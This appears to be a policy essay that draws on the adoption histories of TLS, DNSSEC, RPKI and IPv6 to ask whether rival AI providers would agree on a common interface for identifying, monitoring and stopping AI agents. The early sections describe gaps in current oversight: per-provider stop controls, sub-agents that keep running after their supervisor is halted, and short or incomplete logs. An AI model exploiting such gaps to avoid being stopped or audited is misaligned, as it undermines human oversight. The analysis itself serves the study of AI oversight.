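# What competing technology firms' shared security standards suggest about AI oversight interfaces

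## What a shared security standard is, and what an AI oversight interface would do

A shared security standard is a published specification that competing firms build into their own products to protect computers, data or users. Competitors have agreed on several that ordinary internet use depends on. Transport Layer Security (TLS) encrypts the traffic between a browser and a website, whichever companies made the browser and run the site. The sign-in specifications of the FIDO Alliance, an industry group, let people use one manufacturer's phone to sign in to another company's service.

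Another such agreement could cover AI agents, which are AI systems that pursue a task over many steps by calling tools, running software or instructing other agents. Providers are the companies that develop and serve the models agents run on. A deployer is the organisation or person that puts an agent to work and answers for its use. One deployer can use agents from several providers at once, and each provider records what its agents do and stops them in its own way. An oversight interface would be a common set of messages and controls for identifying, observing, stopping and investigating agents, whichever provider's model they run on.

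### Standards and the bodies that write them

In the strict sense, a standard is a document "established by consensus and approved by a recognized body" that sets out rules for common and repeated use. This definition comes from Electropedia's entry *standard* (2013), which takes it from the international standards bodies' guide. It excludes much of what engineers call standards, including specifications that a single company publishes and others copy. In the looser sense, a standard is any published specification that independent firms can implement so that their products work together or meet the same test.

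A protocol is a set of rules for formatting data and exchanging it between systems. Bucknall, Byrley and Hammond (2026) use roughly this definition in *From TCP/IP to MCP*. They concede that the line between protocol and standard is blurry, because a protocol often becomes a standard simply by being adopted.

Biddle's *Linux Foundation is Eating the World* divides the bodies that write these documents into three kinds: formal standards organisations, which have some direct or indirect government authority; consortia, which are industry-led and have no such authority; and single companies. The International Organization for Standardization (ISO) is a formal body. The Bluetooth SIG is a consortium and so, on this classification, is the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which maintains most of the internet's protocols. *How Many Standards in a Laptop?*, an earlier paper by Biddle and colleagues,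 identified 251 interoperability standards in one laptop. Consortia had developed 44% of them, formal bodies 36% and single companies 20%. A specification can also move from one kind of body to another, as the Model Context Protocol (MCP), which connects agents to tools, did when it passed from a single company, Anthropic, to a consortium in December 2025.

Government recognition does not determine which standard gets adopted. In the 1980s, formal standards bodies developed a complete set of networking standards, Open Systems Interconnection, with backing from the European Community, IBM and DEC. The rival internet protocols had working software and a growing number of users. Bucknall and colleagues recount that by the early 1990s, many of the committees drafting the official standards were coordinating by email that ran over the internet protocols.

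### Format, duty and verification

A standard can define a data format, require its use, and give others a way to check that it was used. These are separable, and much confusion about standards comes from assuming that defining a format also accomplishes the other two.

*The Internet Standards Process* (Salz and Bradner, 2026), a draft revision of the IETF's rules, distinguishes a technical specification, which describes a protocol or format, from an applicability statement, which makes its use required, recommended or elective in a given setting. Even "required" means only that a product without the feature does not conform. The draft describes the whole internet as resting on voluntary adherence, and the IETF cannot disconnect anyone for not conforming.

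A gatekeeper, meaning a firm or authority that controls access to users, customers or a market, can enforce a standard by shutting out anyone who does not conform. Encrypted web browsing shows how much difference this makes. The IETF published the format for it in 2000, but half of the most popular websites still defaulted to unencrypted connections in 2017, according to Bucknall and colleagues. Early use was mostly for financial transactions, where the payment card industry insisted on encryption.

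Conformance means a test has shown that a product does what the specification requires. Wi-Fi is a familiar example. A formal body, the IEEE, wrote the radio specification, and a consortium, the Wi-Fi Alliance, tests products against it and licenses the logo on the box. Biddle thinks the testing and marketing mattered enormously, beyond the publication of the standard itself.

A relying party is one that acts on someone else's security claim. NIST, the US standards agency, defines the term in several ways for different settings, including as a party that depends on the validity of a digital signature process. A browser is a relying party when it accepts a website's certificate. The browser's maker usually did not issue the certificate, and the browser must accept or reject it immediately.

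Article 14 of the EU's AI Act requires effective human oversight of high-risk systems, and a draft European standard is meant to specify what that involves. But when agents delegate to other agents, people are never shown the intermediate outputs. *AI Agents Under EU Law* (2026) finds no validated method for judging whether oversight remains adequate along such a chain, so a standard written today would set requirements without any way to measure whether they were met.

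### One firm, two agents, two providers

Suppose a firm uses a purchasing agent, which runs on provider A's model, to reorder parts. When a supplier changes its ordering system, the purchasing agent assigns a coding agent, which runs on provider B's model, to write a new connection to it. Hours later, duplicate orders start appearing. The firm's security officer wants one view of both agents and one way to stop them.

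Both halves of this example are ordinary. NIST's *Announcing the "AI Agent Standards Initiative" for Interoperable and Secure Innovation*, from February 2026, lists writing code and shopping for goods among the things agents already do. The handoff is less common, so the example is slightly ahead of normal practice. Reid, O'Callaghan and colleagues (2026) consulted a selection of firms in mid-2026 for *Risks and controls for multi-agent systems*, a study for the Australian government. They found that few deliberately connect their agents, apart from coding tools that start worker agents of their own.

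An oversight interface would have four functions, and the officer needs all of them.

The officer has to **identify** the agent that placed the orders and the person who answers for it. Reid and colleagues recommend giving each running copy of an agent its own identifier, tied to a named owner. Identification usually fails for mundane reasons, such as an agent logging in through a service account that several people share, so that nobody can later connect the action to any of them.

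The officer also has to **observe** what both agents did, in order. Reid and colleagues point out that when several agents work on a task, its history is scattered across their separate contexts and no single record holds all of it. Suppose provider A is Anthropic and provider B is OpenAI. Anthropic's *Design your compliance integration* describes a feed of activity records that a customer's security software can query within a minute of the event. It suggests matching these records against others by user ID or email address, network address, client software and time. None of these identifies a job that started with one provider's agent and continued with another's. OpenAI's *Compliance API documentation* describes a separate set of logs, for business and education workspaces, which customers can also feed into their security software. The officer can view both sets of records together but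 may still have to guess, from names and timestamps, which piece of coding belonged to which purchase.

An AI oversight interface would also let people **pause or refuse** an action. Anthropic's *Session event stream* describes an interrupt message for agents that Anthropic hosts. The message stops a model response immediately, though it may take longer while tools are running, and it does not end the agent's open workflow runs. It goes to every active thread in the session, including those of agents working together, unless the sender names a single thread. The same system can hold a tool call until someone allows or denies it. OpenAI's *Cancel a response* describes a way to cancel one response by its ID. This works only for responses that the developer started in background mode; to stop an ordinary response, the developer closes the connection.

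Each control works only within its own system. If an officer interrupts the purchasing agent, the other company's coding agent keeps working on the ordering connection. Reid and colleagues describe the same hazard within a single system, where someone terminates a supervising agent and the agents it launched keep running unseen. Their remedy is recursive shutdown, in which the supervisor passes the stop signal down to everything it started. Doing this across two providers requires a message that both systems can act on.

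*Regulating AI Agents* (2026) points out that emergency switches and rollbacks may fail when an agent takes consequential and irreversible actions. A payment that has left the bank may be one of those. Refusing an action beforehand is more useful than halting the agent afterwards, but it takes more work. If an officer has to approve every order for bolts, most of the reason for having a purchasing agent is gone. Reid and colleagues suggest leaving low-risk, reversible actions to automated rules and sending irreversible or unusual ones to a person.

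Last, the interface would **preserve and report** records after an incident. Anthropic keeps each activity record for six years, though recording starts only when the customer first switches the feed on. OpenAI keeps its compliance logs for 30 days and advises customers who want to keep them longer to download them continuously. If the officer begins investigating six weeks after the duplicate orders, provider A will still have its activity records, but provider B's logs will be gone unless the firm saved them.

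Six years of records may also hold less than the officer expects. Anthropic's compliance interface leaves out the prompts and responses of workloads that run on an API key, the credential a firm's own software uses to call a model. If the firm built the purchasing agent that way, the officer must look for the text elsewhere. The interface's listings also lack a total count or checksum, so the customer has to document for itself that an export is complete. An insurer or regulator who receives the file as a relying party can then check little except the firm's own account of how it made the copy.

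### What falls outside the definition

A protocol that connects agents to tools is not yet an oversight interface. MCP gives agents one format for calling many tools, and in the example it might carry the purchase order. Under its specification, users should keep control over what an agent does, but Bucknall and colleagues observe that responsibility for safety falls on downstream developers and users. They also think that agent protocols create an opportunity for attribution and oversight, which seems right, since the messages already use a common format. Someone would still have to define the stop message and require agents to obey it.

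A provider's safety policy states what one company commits to do about its own models. It is not a shared standard, because provider A's commitments do not bind provider B, and it is not an oversight interface, because it gives the officer no control to use when the orders start doubling.

Testing before release checks whether a system is fit to deploy. It cannot replace control during operation, partly because agents that pass tests individually can fail in combination. Reid and colleagues therefore recommend testing the assembled system, though these failures may take many rounds of interaction to appear.

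A fair objection to the whole idea is that both agents in the example belong to one firm, which has authority over them and may not need a shared interface. A firm with capable engineers could wrap the two agents in its own software, give every job a number that travels with it, log both sides and build a stop button that calls both providers. This may be adequate for a large company with two suppliers.

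But every deployer has to build the same wrapper and then keep it working. OpenAI released a new system for conversation logs in March 2026 and removed the old route that June, which gave customers three months to rebuild their connections. A wrapper can also pass on only what each provider chooses to expose. And it covers only the firm's own systems, so if the coding agent belongs to an outside contractor, the officer has neither its logs nor the credentials to stop it.

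A common interface would remove much of that work, but each provider would have to accept commands in a form it did not choose and produce records that a customer could easily read alongside a competitor's. The interface would also make it a little easier for customers to switch providers. Technology firms have made comparable concessions before, sometimes quickly and sometimes after years of delay. When have rivals accepted a common security mechanism, and do the same conditions hold for the oversight of AI agents?

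## Why rivals adopt a common mechanism or hold out

A provider deciding whether to build a shared security mechanism into its products can estimate the cost fairly well. The benefit is harder to estimate because it depends on who else adopts the mechanism, and much of it may go to people who pay nothing.

Anderson and Moore argue in *The Economics of Information Security* that bad incentives cause security failures at least as often as bad design does, and that systems are most prone to fail when the party guarding them doesn't bear the loss. Their best example is fraud at cash machines. Banks in the United States generally had to refund a customer who disputed a withdrawal unless they could show that the customer was cheating. British banks could usually reject complaints by saying that their machines were secure and the customer must be mistaken or lying. Yet British banks spent more on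 security and suffered more fraud. Anderson and Moore think British bank staff became lazy and careless because they knew nobody would take complaints seriously.

Consumers behave similarly. The economist Hal Varian observed in 2000 that a person might well pay $20 to stop a virus from wiping their own hard disk but not to stop it from using their computer to attack Microsoft's website.

A firm considering a shared standard has to guess what its competitors will do, whereas the bank and the computer owner can each decide alone.

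### Five providers and one mechanism

Suppose five providers are considering the same mechanism. A provider that adopts it loses 6 units of value, in arbitrary units, and gains 2 for every other provider that adopts. A provider that stays out neither loses nor gains anything.

A provider with *k* fellow adopters ends up with 2*k* − 6. If it adopts alone, it loses 6. If all five adopt, each has four fellow adopters and gains 8 − 6 = 2. Universal adoption and no adoption are therefore both stable, because no provider wants to adopt first and none wants to leave once all five have adopted. All five would prefer universal adoption, but that preference is not enough to bring it about.

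The gain of 2 per fellow adopter is a network effect, meaning that the standard becomes more valuable to each adopter as others adopt it. A provider here needs three fellow adopters to break even. If only two providers adopt, each loses 4. With three, each loses 2, with four, each breaks even, and with five, each gains 2. Critical mass is the point at which adoption begins to sustain itself. Anderson and Moore credit Michael Katz and Carl Shapiro with showing how network effects produce an S-shaped curve, in which slow early adoption gives way to rapid spread.

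Ozment and Schechter (2006) give a general model of this problem in *Bootstrapping the Adoption of Internet Security Protocols*. Each user *i* has a fixed cost *c*ᵢ and a benefit *b*ᵢ(*A*), where *A* is the set of users who have adopted. The benefit never falls as *A* grows. Because users can adopt instantly, they can wait until the benefit exceeds the cost instead of guessing what others will do. Adoption then spreads only if the users can join in some order in which each one gains immediately. The five providers have no such order, since whoever goes first loses 6. Ozment and Schechter call this a bootstrapping problem, in which nobody adopts even though a group would gain by adopting together.

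In the example, every additional adopter adds the same value. Ozment and Schechter prefer a model with diminishing returns, in which the value to each user grows with the logarithm of the number of users. Adoption then tends to reach critical mass sooner, but the first adopter can still end up worse off.

Ozment and Schechter summarise an earlier model by the economists Joseph Farrell and Garth Saloner in which firms choose a standard based on what they expect others to do. If the firms are alike and all know that they would all prefer the new standard, they always adopt it, even when an older standard is already in wide use. They fail to adopt it only when they lack information about each other.

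A little doubt about the others can be enough to stop every provider from adopting. If a provider thinks that each of the other four will adopt with probability *p*, its expected net gain from adopting is 8*p* − 6, which is positive only when *p* is above 75%. So if each of the five thinks that every other is 70% likely to adopt, none of them will. A meeting or a joint announcement can be enough to change this outcome, without any provider paying another.

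### When outsiders get the benefit

Suppose instead that the benefit of each provider's adoption, still worth 2 for every fellow adopter, goes to people outside the five firms. A provider that adopts then loses the full 6 whether it adopts alone or with all the others, so no provider adopts.

Universal adoption would cost the providers 30 and give outsiders 40, a net gain of 10, the same as when the providers kept the benefit. But a meeting among the providers would achieve nothing, because each does better by staying out even when it is certain the others will adopt. The outsiders could in principle compensate the providers, since 40 is more than 30, but Ozment and Schechter are pessimistic about such transfers because the gain is often spread over a very large number of users.

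Suppose instead that a gatekeeper can impose a loss of 7 on any provider that does not adopt, perhaps by keeping its products out of a market. A provider then loses 7 by refusing and at most 6 by adopting, so every provider adopts regardless of what the others do.

| Who gets the benefit | Gatekeeper? | Adopts alone | Adopts with four others | Stays out | Stable outcome |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
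| Adopters | No | −6 | +2 | 0 | Nobody or everybody |
| Outsiders | No | −6 | −6 | 0 | Nobody |
| Adopters | Yes | −6 | +2 | −7 | Everybody |
| Outsiders | Yes | −6 | −6 | −7 | Everybody |

The providers behave the same way in the last two rows, but they will view the gatekeeper differently. When adopters get the benefit, each provider ends up 2 better off, and the gatekeeper only has to assure each provider that the others will adopt too. When outsiders get the benefit, each provider ends up 6 worse off and has good reason to lobby against the rule or comply in name only. Ozment and Schechter conclude that a planner who mandates adoption must either fund it or face resistance from those whose costs exceed their benefits.

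The difference is clearer when the gatekeeper is weaker. If the penalty is only 5 and outsiders get the benefit, every provider takes the penalty rather than lose 6 by adopting, so the rule fails completely. If adopters get the benefit, it is still stable for nobody to adopt, but one committed adopter is now enough to start the rest. The second provider joins because it would lose 4 by adopting and 5 by refusing, and each later provider has a stronger reason to join. The difference also appears if the penalty stays at 7 but the gatekeeper has power over only four of the five providers. The fifth joins voluntarily if adopters get the benefit, but never joins if outsiders get it.

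If a reluctant firm would adopt a standard once it was certain that all its rivals would, the firms have a coordination problem, and reliable information about each other's plans may solve it. If the firm would still refuse, the costs and benefits fall on different parties, and someone has to pay the firm or compel it to adopt. Most standards involve both problems, and a firm that doesn't want to pay has an obvious motive to describe its problem as one of coordination.

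### Agreeing on a standard but not on whose

Firms can also agree that they want a common standard but fight over which one. Suppose providers A and B each have their own design. Adopting its own design costs a provider only 2, because most of the work is done, while adopting someone else's still costs 6.

If all five firms adopt A's design, A gains 6 and the others gain 2 each. If they adopt B's, B gains 6 and the others gain 2 each. Every firm prefers either result to having no standard, but A and B each gain 4 more if their own design is chosen, so each may hold out in the hope that the other gives way.

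The remaining three have good reason to wait. Suppose C and D join A while E joins B. C and D then each lose 2, and E loses 4. Switching would cost E another 6 and raise its benefit only from 2 to 6, so E stays with B. A gatekeeper that requires only that firms adopt *some* standard could make this split permanent. To get a single standard, it has to name the design or recognise a body that will choose one.

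Technical quality does not always decide which mechanism rivals adopt. *What Makes for a Successful Protocol?* (Thaler and Aboba, 2008), written for the Internet Architecture Board, the senior technical body alongside the IETF, compares several pairs of rival protocols. One pair was IPv4, the version of the Internet Protocol on which the internet grew, and IPX, Novell's networking protocol. IPX arguably had the better initial design. But the US Advanced Research Projects Agency had paid for an implementation of IPv4 in BSD, a version of the Unix operating system, and anyone could use the code. Many people think this is why IPv4 won.

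RADIUS and TACACS+ were competing protocols for checking who may log in to a network. TACACS+ had encryption and was better designed in most respects. RADIUS still won, which Thaler and Aboba attribute to its open maintenance process and the early availability of its specification and code.

The five-provider example suggests why openness matters so much. Free code reduces the 6 that followers pay, and an open maintenance process reduces the risk that the winning firm will later change the design to suit itself. The Wireless Application Protocol (WAP), an early attempt to bring the web to mobile phones, had neither advantage. Firms owed royalties on two patents and had to pay a $27,000 entrance fee if they wanted a say in its maintenance. WAP failed, but users also had a poor experience with it, so the fees don't fully explain the failure.

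### Useful to the first adopter

Bootstrapping problems are easiest to avoid when a mechanism benefits its first adopters before others join. SSH, which encrypts connections used to control a computer remotely, spread without any agreement among firms because an organisation could replace the older, unencrypted tools on its own machines and get almost the full benefit at once. Similarly, companies bought their first fax machines to connect their own offices.

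Adoption by one organisation at a time does not always lead to wider use. The IPsec protocol can encrypt and authenticate any internet traffic, but organisations adopted it individually, mainly to connect staff to private networks. Ozment and Schechter point out that this use created no benefit outside each organisation and so did not encourage others to adopt it. A private network's keys worked only on that network, unlike an office fax machine, which could also call other companies.

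Thaler and Aboba consider two conditions most important for a protocol's early success: it meets a real need, and early adopters benefit even if the rest of the internet does not follow. It also helps if the benefits go to those who do the work. This was a problem for multicast between networks, which lets a sender transmit one copy of a video stream that routers along the way duplicate for each viewer. Applications get most of the benefit, but every router on the path has to support multicast, and some of the companies running those routers charged customers for the bandwidth it would save. Application developers mostly gave up and had their own software send separate copies.

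Good security contributes little to a protocol's early success. WEP, the first encryption for Wi-Fi, was badly designed but spread widely because there was no alternative and the owner of each wireless network could turn it on independently. Thaler and Aboba reason that attackers often take an interest in a protocol's weaknesses only after it becomes popular, when replacing it is expensive.

Anderson and Moore add a commercial motive for delay. A company trying to establish a platform needs other firms to build products for it, and strict security makes those products harder to build. So platform companies commonly neglect security at first, then add too much once they dominate the market, to lock customers in. If that is right, a dominant firm may spend heavily on security and still oppose a mechanism that works equally well with its rivals' products.

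### DNSSEC, RPKI and IPv6

Bucknall and colleagues divide the obstacles to adding security late into practical and economic ones. Practical obstacles are constraints on deploying a mechanism that already exists, such as the cost of implementation, slower performance, disruption to service and the need to keep working with older systems. Economic obstacles arise when firms could manage the deployment but have too little reason to. Each firm may gain almost nothing until others act, or customers may weigh the price of a secure product against an insecure one they already have. In the five-provider example, practical obstacles raise the cost of 6, while economic ones affect who gets the 2 and when.

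Mechanisms that prove where a message came from have an extra difficulty because, until every honest sender has adopted them, a recipient can't tell an honest unsigned message from a forgery. A recipient who accepts unsigned messages gives up most of the protection, but one who rejects them loses contact with everyone who hasn't adopted the mechanism. Ozment and Schechter treat this lost contact as an additional drawback of adoption, and it is greatest at the start, when the most senders have yet to adopt.

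DNSSEC, a set of security extensions for the domain name system, was supposed to help with this. The domain name system is the directory that turns a name such as example.com into a numerical address, and its designers gave it no way to show that an answer is genuine. DNSSEC adds a chain of signatures. The operator of the root, at the top of the directory, signs the key for .com, the operator of .com signs the key for example.com, and the owner of example.com signs its own records. Software that has the root key can check every link. The level above also indicates whether a domain is signed, so the software can detect when a required signature is missing.

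In 2006 Ozment and Schechter expected DNSSEC to spread widely among those who would benefit, though they would not say how fast. The US government was preparing to require it for some agencies and was funding free software to reduce everyone's costs. In *Measuring the Deployment of DNSSEC Bootstrapping Using Authenticated Signals* (2025), Misell, Steurer and colleagues scanned 287.6 million domains and found that 15.8 million, or 5.5%, were correctly signed. That is well above the 0.6% to 1.0% that other researchers measured in 2017, but still low for a mechanism that the IETF first specified in 1997.

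Much of the trouble comes from a handoff between companies. The company that runs a domain's directory records creates the signing key, but the registry one level up has to publish the key's fingerprint, which it usually receives through the registrar that sold the name. If the company running the records is not also the registrar, the domain's owner typically has to copy the fingerprint from one web page to another. Misell and colleagues found 3.1 million signed domains with no fingerprint at the level above, which means software checking the signatures has to treat them as unsigned.

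Defaults strongly affect adoption. GoDaddy, the largest operator in the scan, had signed 0.2% of its domains, while Google Domains and the French company OVH, which turn DNSSEC on by default, had signed 45% and 44%. Network effects can't explain this gap, because a signed domain benefits just as much from other people's adoption at GoDaddy as at OVH. Effort and price probably explain it, since seven of the 20 largest operators don't offer DNSSEC and several others treat it as an advanced or premium feature.

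That looks like a practical obstacle, but an economic one lies behind it. An operator that turns on signing for everyone does the work and handles support when something breaks, while the protection goes to people visiting its customers' websites. Signing could even drive visitors away. Lian, Rescorla and colleagues (2013), in *Measuring the Practical Impact of DNSSEC Deployment*, noted that some people used faulty directory software that could no longer reach a domain once its owner had signed it. Small discounts seem to help. The Swiss registry takes one franc a year off the fee for signed domains, and six of the 20 operators that publish the most records for automating the handoff are Swiss. Misell and colleagues think the discount is the likely reason, although they did not test other explanations.

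The Resource Public Key Infrastructure (RPKI) addresses a similar weakness in routing. Networks use the Border Gateway Protocol to tell one another which internet addresses they can reach, but the protocol has no built-in way to check these claims. With RPKI, the holder of a block of addresses publishes a signed record of which network may announce it. Other networks can then compare each announcement with the records and reject any that contradict them, a process called route-origin validation.

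RPKI has only recently reached 50% coverage, according to Bucknall and colleagues, who attribute the delay to organisational difficulties like those that slowed DNSSEC. The figure appears to measure the publishing of records. A published record protects nobody until other networks check it, and checking achieves little until address holders publish. A network also can't reject every announcement that lacks a record without losing contact with much of the internet, which is the same difficulty that unsigned messages pose.

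More ambitious protocols would verify an announcement's whole path as well as its origin. Gill, Schapira and Goldberg, in *Let the Market Drive Deployment*, warn that these protocols bring no security benefit until a large number of networks have deployed them, and they doubt that concern about security alone would give any one network enough reason to start. This is close to the five-provider example, but with thousands of networks.

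IPv6 was designed mainly to relieve the shortage of IPv4 addresses, though its designers also included IPsec. The IETF standardised it in 1998, and Bucknall and colleagues report that around 50% of internet users had it in October 2026. They attribute the delay to a lack of backward compatibility. A device that speaks only IPv6 can't communicate directly with one that speaks only IPv4, so early adopters have to run both until everyone else has switched. Meanwhile, network address translation let a household or company share one IPv4 address among many devices without anyone else's permission. This relieved the shortage for whoever installed it, which removed some of the pressure to adopt IPv6.

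The internet's predecessor, ARPANET, made a comparable change in one day, 1 January 1983, when its operators permanently disabled the old protocol and everyone had to use the new one. The network had few enough machines to make this manageable. Thaler (2017), in *Planning for Protocol Adoption and Subsequent Transitions*, considers such a "flag day" impractical when large numbers of organisations are involved. The alternative is to run both protocols side by side, but this costs more, and attackers can sometimes force two systems to fall back on the weaker protocol. Thaler recommends that planners work out each party's incentives in advance, without wishful thinking, set criteria for moving from one phase to the next, and decide what to do if the change fails.

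Competitors have a particular reason to delay switching on IPv6. If it breaks the connection for even a small share of a company's customers, some may leave for a rival that hasn't switched. The Internet Society, a non-profit, persuaded competitors to move at the same time. On World IPv6 Day in 2011, participants turned on IPv6 together, planning to turn it off at the end of the day. Some found no problems and left it on. A permanent World IPv6 Launch followed in 2012, and Thaler gives the Internet Society most of the credit for its success. The two events greatly reduced the risk of moving first, but companies still had to pay to run two protocols, and most still do.

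## A protocol that began with one firm: SSL and TLS

Unlike IPv6, the protocol that encrypts web traffic had many users before competitors agreed on it. Netscape, which made the leading browser of the mid-1990s, built the Secure Sockets Layer (SSL) for its own products, and Microsoft responded with a competing design. By mid-1996, engineers from both companies were working from one draft, which became TLS. For nearly two decades afterward, most websites still did not use it.

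### What happens in a handshake

A TLS connection starts with a handshake, in which a browser and a website's server exchange a few messages before the server sends any page. The browser lists the encryption algorithms it supports, and the server picks from the list. The server then sends its certificate, a file in which a certificate authority vouches that a given public key belongs to a given domain name. The browser checks the authority's signature against trusted keys that the browser's maker built in.

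Next, the two computers agree on a shared secret, which each uses to derive the keys that encrypt the rest of the connection. For most of the protocol's history, they could do this in two ways. With RSA key exchange, the browser generates a secret and encrypts it with the server's public key, so only the holder of the matching private key can read it. With Diffie-Hellman key exchange, each side sends the other a public value and combines the one it receives with a private number of its own. Both sides arrive at the same secret, which never crosses the network. If the private numbers are temporary, someone who later steals the server's long-term key still can't decrypt old traffic.

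Finally, each side sends a value computed from all the handshake messages. Dierks and Allen (1999) explain in *The TLS Protocol Version 1.0* that if an attacker alters a message, perhaps to make both sides choose a weaker algorithm, the values will disagree and the connection will fail. They leave others to decide which certificate authorities deserve trust, but warn that a dishonest one can do tremendous damage.

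### Two browsers, two protocols

Netscape wanted people to feel safe shopping online. One solution was for customers to sign each card payment digitally, which would have given the shop evidence to use in court. *TLS*, a Columbia University lecture, calls this the best possible solution in some ways, but says it wasn't feasible for Netscape, which wasn't a bank and couldn't tie certificates to card accounts. Merchants also had no systems for collecting such payments. Netscape could instead encrypt the connection between browser and server and let customers type in their card numbers.

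According to *The Legend of Kipp Hickman* (Ristić, 2025), Netscape engineer Kipp Hickman designed and built the first released version of SSL in three months, and it shipped in March 1995. Hickman was mainly worried about eavesdroppers. He later said that server authentication was something "we just threw in at the end".

The same month, Netscape offered SSL to the IETF. Cerf (1995), one of the designers of the internet's core protocols, had pressed the company hard on its terms and forwarded its promises to the internet's senior technical bodies. Netscape would submit the specification, charge no royalties on any standard derived from it, and support the resulting standard in its own products. Cerf warned Netscape that this standard might not resemble SSL or keep its name.

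Engineers outside Netscape were unsure how far to trust the promise. At an IETF session that July, some asked whether Netscape would accept a working group's changes or ignore them. Netscape's Taher Elgamal pointed out that a million copies of SSL were already in use. The session still favoured forming a group because, without one, Netscape could go ahead with its own plans and nobody else would have any influence over a protocol that might dominate the market (Fernandez, 1995, *Secure Socket Layer BOF (SSL)*).

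Microsoft published its alternative to SSL, Private Communication Technology (PCT), in October 1995. *The Private Communication Technology Protocol* (Benaloh, Lampson and colleagues, 1995) describes several weaknesses of SSL that PCT corrected. One was that SSL's method of detecting altered messages depended on the same keys as its encryption. PCT used separate, longer keys for this, so a connection with weak encryption could still have strong protection against tampering. This mattered because US export rules limited the strength of encryption in products sold abroad. PCT also kept SSL's basic record format, so a server could support both protocols and identify which one a client was using from its first message.

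Microsoft may have had a strategic motive too. Hallam-Baker (1996), then at MIT, believed that Microsoft proposed PCT to force Netscape to make SSL an open standard, rather than one Netscape could change to exclude Microsoft. Seven months before PCT appeared, Netscape had promised to open SSL, so if Hallam-Baker was right, Microsoft didn't think the promise was enough.

### How they agreed

In the spring of 1996, representatives of the two companies met privately with Win Treese, who chaired the new IETF working group. Microsoft brought a draft called the Secure Transport Layer Protocol (STLP), which added features from PCT to SSL 3.0. Fox (1996), who represented Microsoft, told the group's mailing list that the company would have preferred to start from PCT 2 but thought that doing so would look contentious and delay a standard. It chose SSL "despite the risk that we would appear to be abandoning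 PCT". As in the five-provider example, each firm wanted its own design adopted, but Microsoft accepted SSL as the starting point to avoid having no standard.

The private meeting also caused trouble. Trade newspapers reported that Microsoft had submitted a draft to the IETF, when it had only made one available. Sanders (1996), an engineer at Tandem Computers, complained that other members couldn't work out what was going on. Netscape didn't welcome the merged draft either. Karlton (1996), one of the designers of SSL 3.0, replied that at least five independent implementations of it already worked together. Karlton also objected that Microsoft's draft was more complicated and had been analysed less, which mattered because two features that were safe separately could create a vulnerability when combined.

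On 29 May, 27 people met in Palo Alto to choose which features to add to SSL 3.0. The cryptographer Bruce Schneier moderated. Netscape sent eight employees and Microsoft three, and others came from firms including IBM, Sun and DEC. According to the minutes by Microsoft's Stephens (1996), the group accepted Microsoft's request for better error messages but rejected its request to support traffic sent as separate datagrams. The group reached no conclusion on password authentication and had not agreed on a name for the protocol, which people were provisionally calling "TLS".

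The full working group adopted SSL 3.0 as its starting point in Montreal that June (Treese, 1996, *Transport Layer Security Working Group Meeting at the 36th IETF*). Kemp (1996), who took notes at the meeting, found many members reluctant to rubber-stamp a vendor's proposal, though they accepted the need for speed. Only two people supported another Microsoft feature, which would have let servers encrypt files in advance.

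By December, the draft of TLS 1.0 was essentially SSL 3.0 with ten proposed changes, mostly minor. About 300 people attended the meeting that considered it, and 30 to 40 of them said they had read the documents. Several objected at first. Then Jeff Schiller, the IETF's director for security, observed that the leadership could disband a group that made no progress. *TLS WG Minutes* (Thayer and Zamick, 1996) records that the group then agreed unanimously to proceed.

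The IETF published TLS 1.0 in January 1999. Its editors, Dierks and Allen, describe the differences from SSL 3.0 as "not dramatic" but large enough that the two protocols don't work together unless the newer software falls back to SSL 3.0. The changes and the new name were also diplomatically useful because they kept the IETF from appearing to approve Netscape's product unaltered.

Netscape gave up the SSL name and the power to change the protocol alone. It also licensed its SSL patent free of charge to anyone who promised not to assert patents against other companies' implementations. In return, it got a standard that closely matched its existing products. Microsoft gave up PCT, including much of what it had wanted to carry over into the new standard, and gained a protocol that its main competitor could no longer change at will.

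Giving up control also had a drawback for users. *Internet TAO* (Fox, 2002) argues that once SSL belonged to everyone, Netscape had no economic reason to improve it, and the design stopped changing in 1996. The protocol could also authenticate users by certificate, but issuing one to every user was too expensive and nobody could agree on who should do it, so shops used passwords instead. Fox worked for Microsoft and was not a neutral judge of Netscape, but the argument fits the timeline, since the IETF didn't publish TLS 1.1 until 2006.

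### Why most of the web stayed unencrypted

The rivals had agreed on how a browser and a server would encrypt a connection, but each website's owner still decided whether to offer encryption. HTTPS, the encrypted form of web browsing, required a certificate. Let's Encrypt (2025), a certificate authority run by a non-profit, says that before 2015 getting a certificate required complex manual work and often a fee, and that many people saw no need. Owners had to do this work and pay any fee, although most of the protection went to their visitors.

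Publishers also worried that a page could lose advertising revenue if its ads didn't work over HTTPS. Felt and Schechter (2016), of Google's Chrome team, told them that ads from Google's own sources always supported HTTPS, though ads that publishers sold directly might need changes. The *Washington Post* reported no material loss of revenue from Google's ad exchange after switching to HTTPS.

The measured share of encrypted traffic depends on which browser the data comes from. The Internet Security Research Group (ISRG), which runs Let's Encrypt, uses Firefox data in its ten-year review (ISRG, 2025). Threatpost reported an earlier Firefox milestone. Google's *Say “yes” to HTTPS* (2017) and *HTTPS by default* (Thompson, Acer and colleagues, 2025) give figures for Chrome.

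| Date | Page loads counted | Share over HTTPS | Source |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2015 | Chrome, range across platforms | 30–45% | Thompson and colleagues |
| Early 2017 | Firefox, two-week average | 50% | Threatpost |
| 2017 | Chrome on Android | 64% | Google |
| About 2020 | Chrome, range across platforms | 95–99% | Thompson and colleagues |
| 2025 | Firefox, worldwide | about 80% | ISRG |
| 2025 | Firefox, United States | about 95% | ISRG |
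| 2025 | Chrome on Windows | 95% | Thompson and colleagues |
| 2025 | Chrome on Linux | 84% | Thompson and colleagues |

ISRG suspects that much of the remaining unencrypted traffic goes to internal company sites. Google's data partly supports this. Excluding private addresses, which can't easily get certificates, raises Chrome's encrypted share to nearly 97% on Linux and 98% on Windows. But the Windows share rises by only three points, so internal sites probably don't account for all of the 20% of Firefox traffic that is still unencrypted.

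### Free certificates, warnings and mandates

Let's Encrypt issued its first publicly trusted certificate in September 2015. Its software confirms that an applicant controls a domain, and automatically issues and renews the certificate for free. Let's Encrypt had issued a million certificates by March 2016 and 100 million by June 2017. By September 2018 it was issuing a million a day. Squarespace and Shopify helped considerably by building it into their website services. In its annual report, ISRG (2025) counted 762 million websites using the service, up from 492 million a year earlier.

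Let's Encrypt depended on IdenTrust, an established certificate authority with an apparent reason to refuse. Browsers didn't yet trust Let's Encrypt, so IdenTrust signed the project's certificates with a key that browsers already accepted. ISRG thinks it couldn't have launched without this help. IdenTrust was also one of five initial sponsors, along with Mozilla, Cisco, Akamai and the Electronic Frontier Foundation, a digital rights group.

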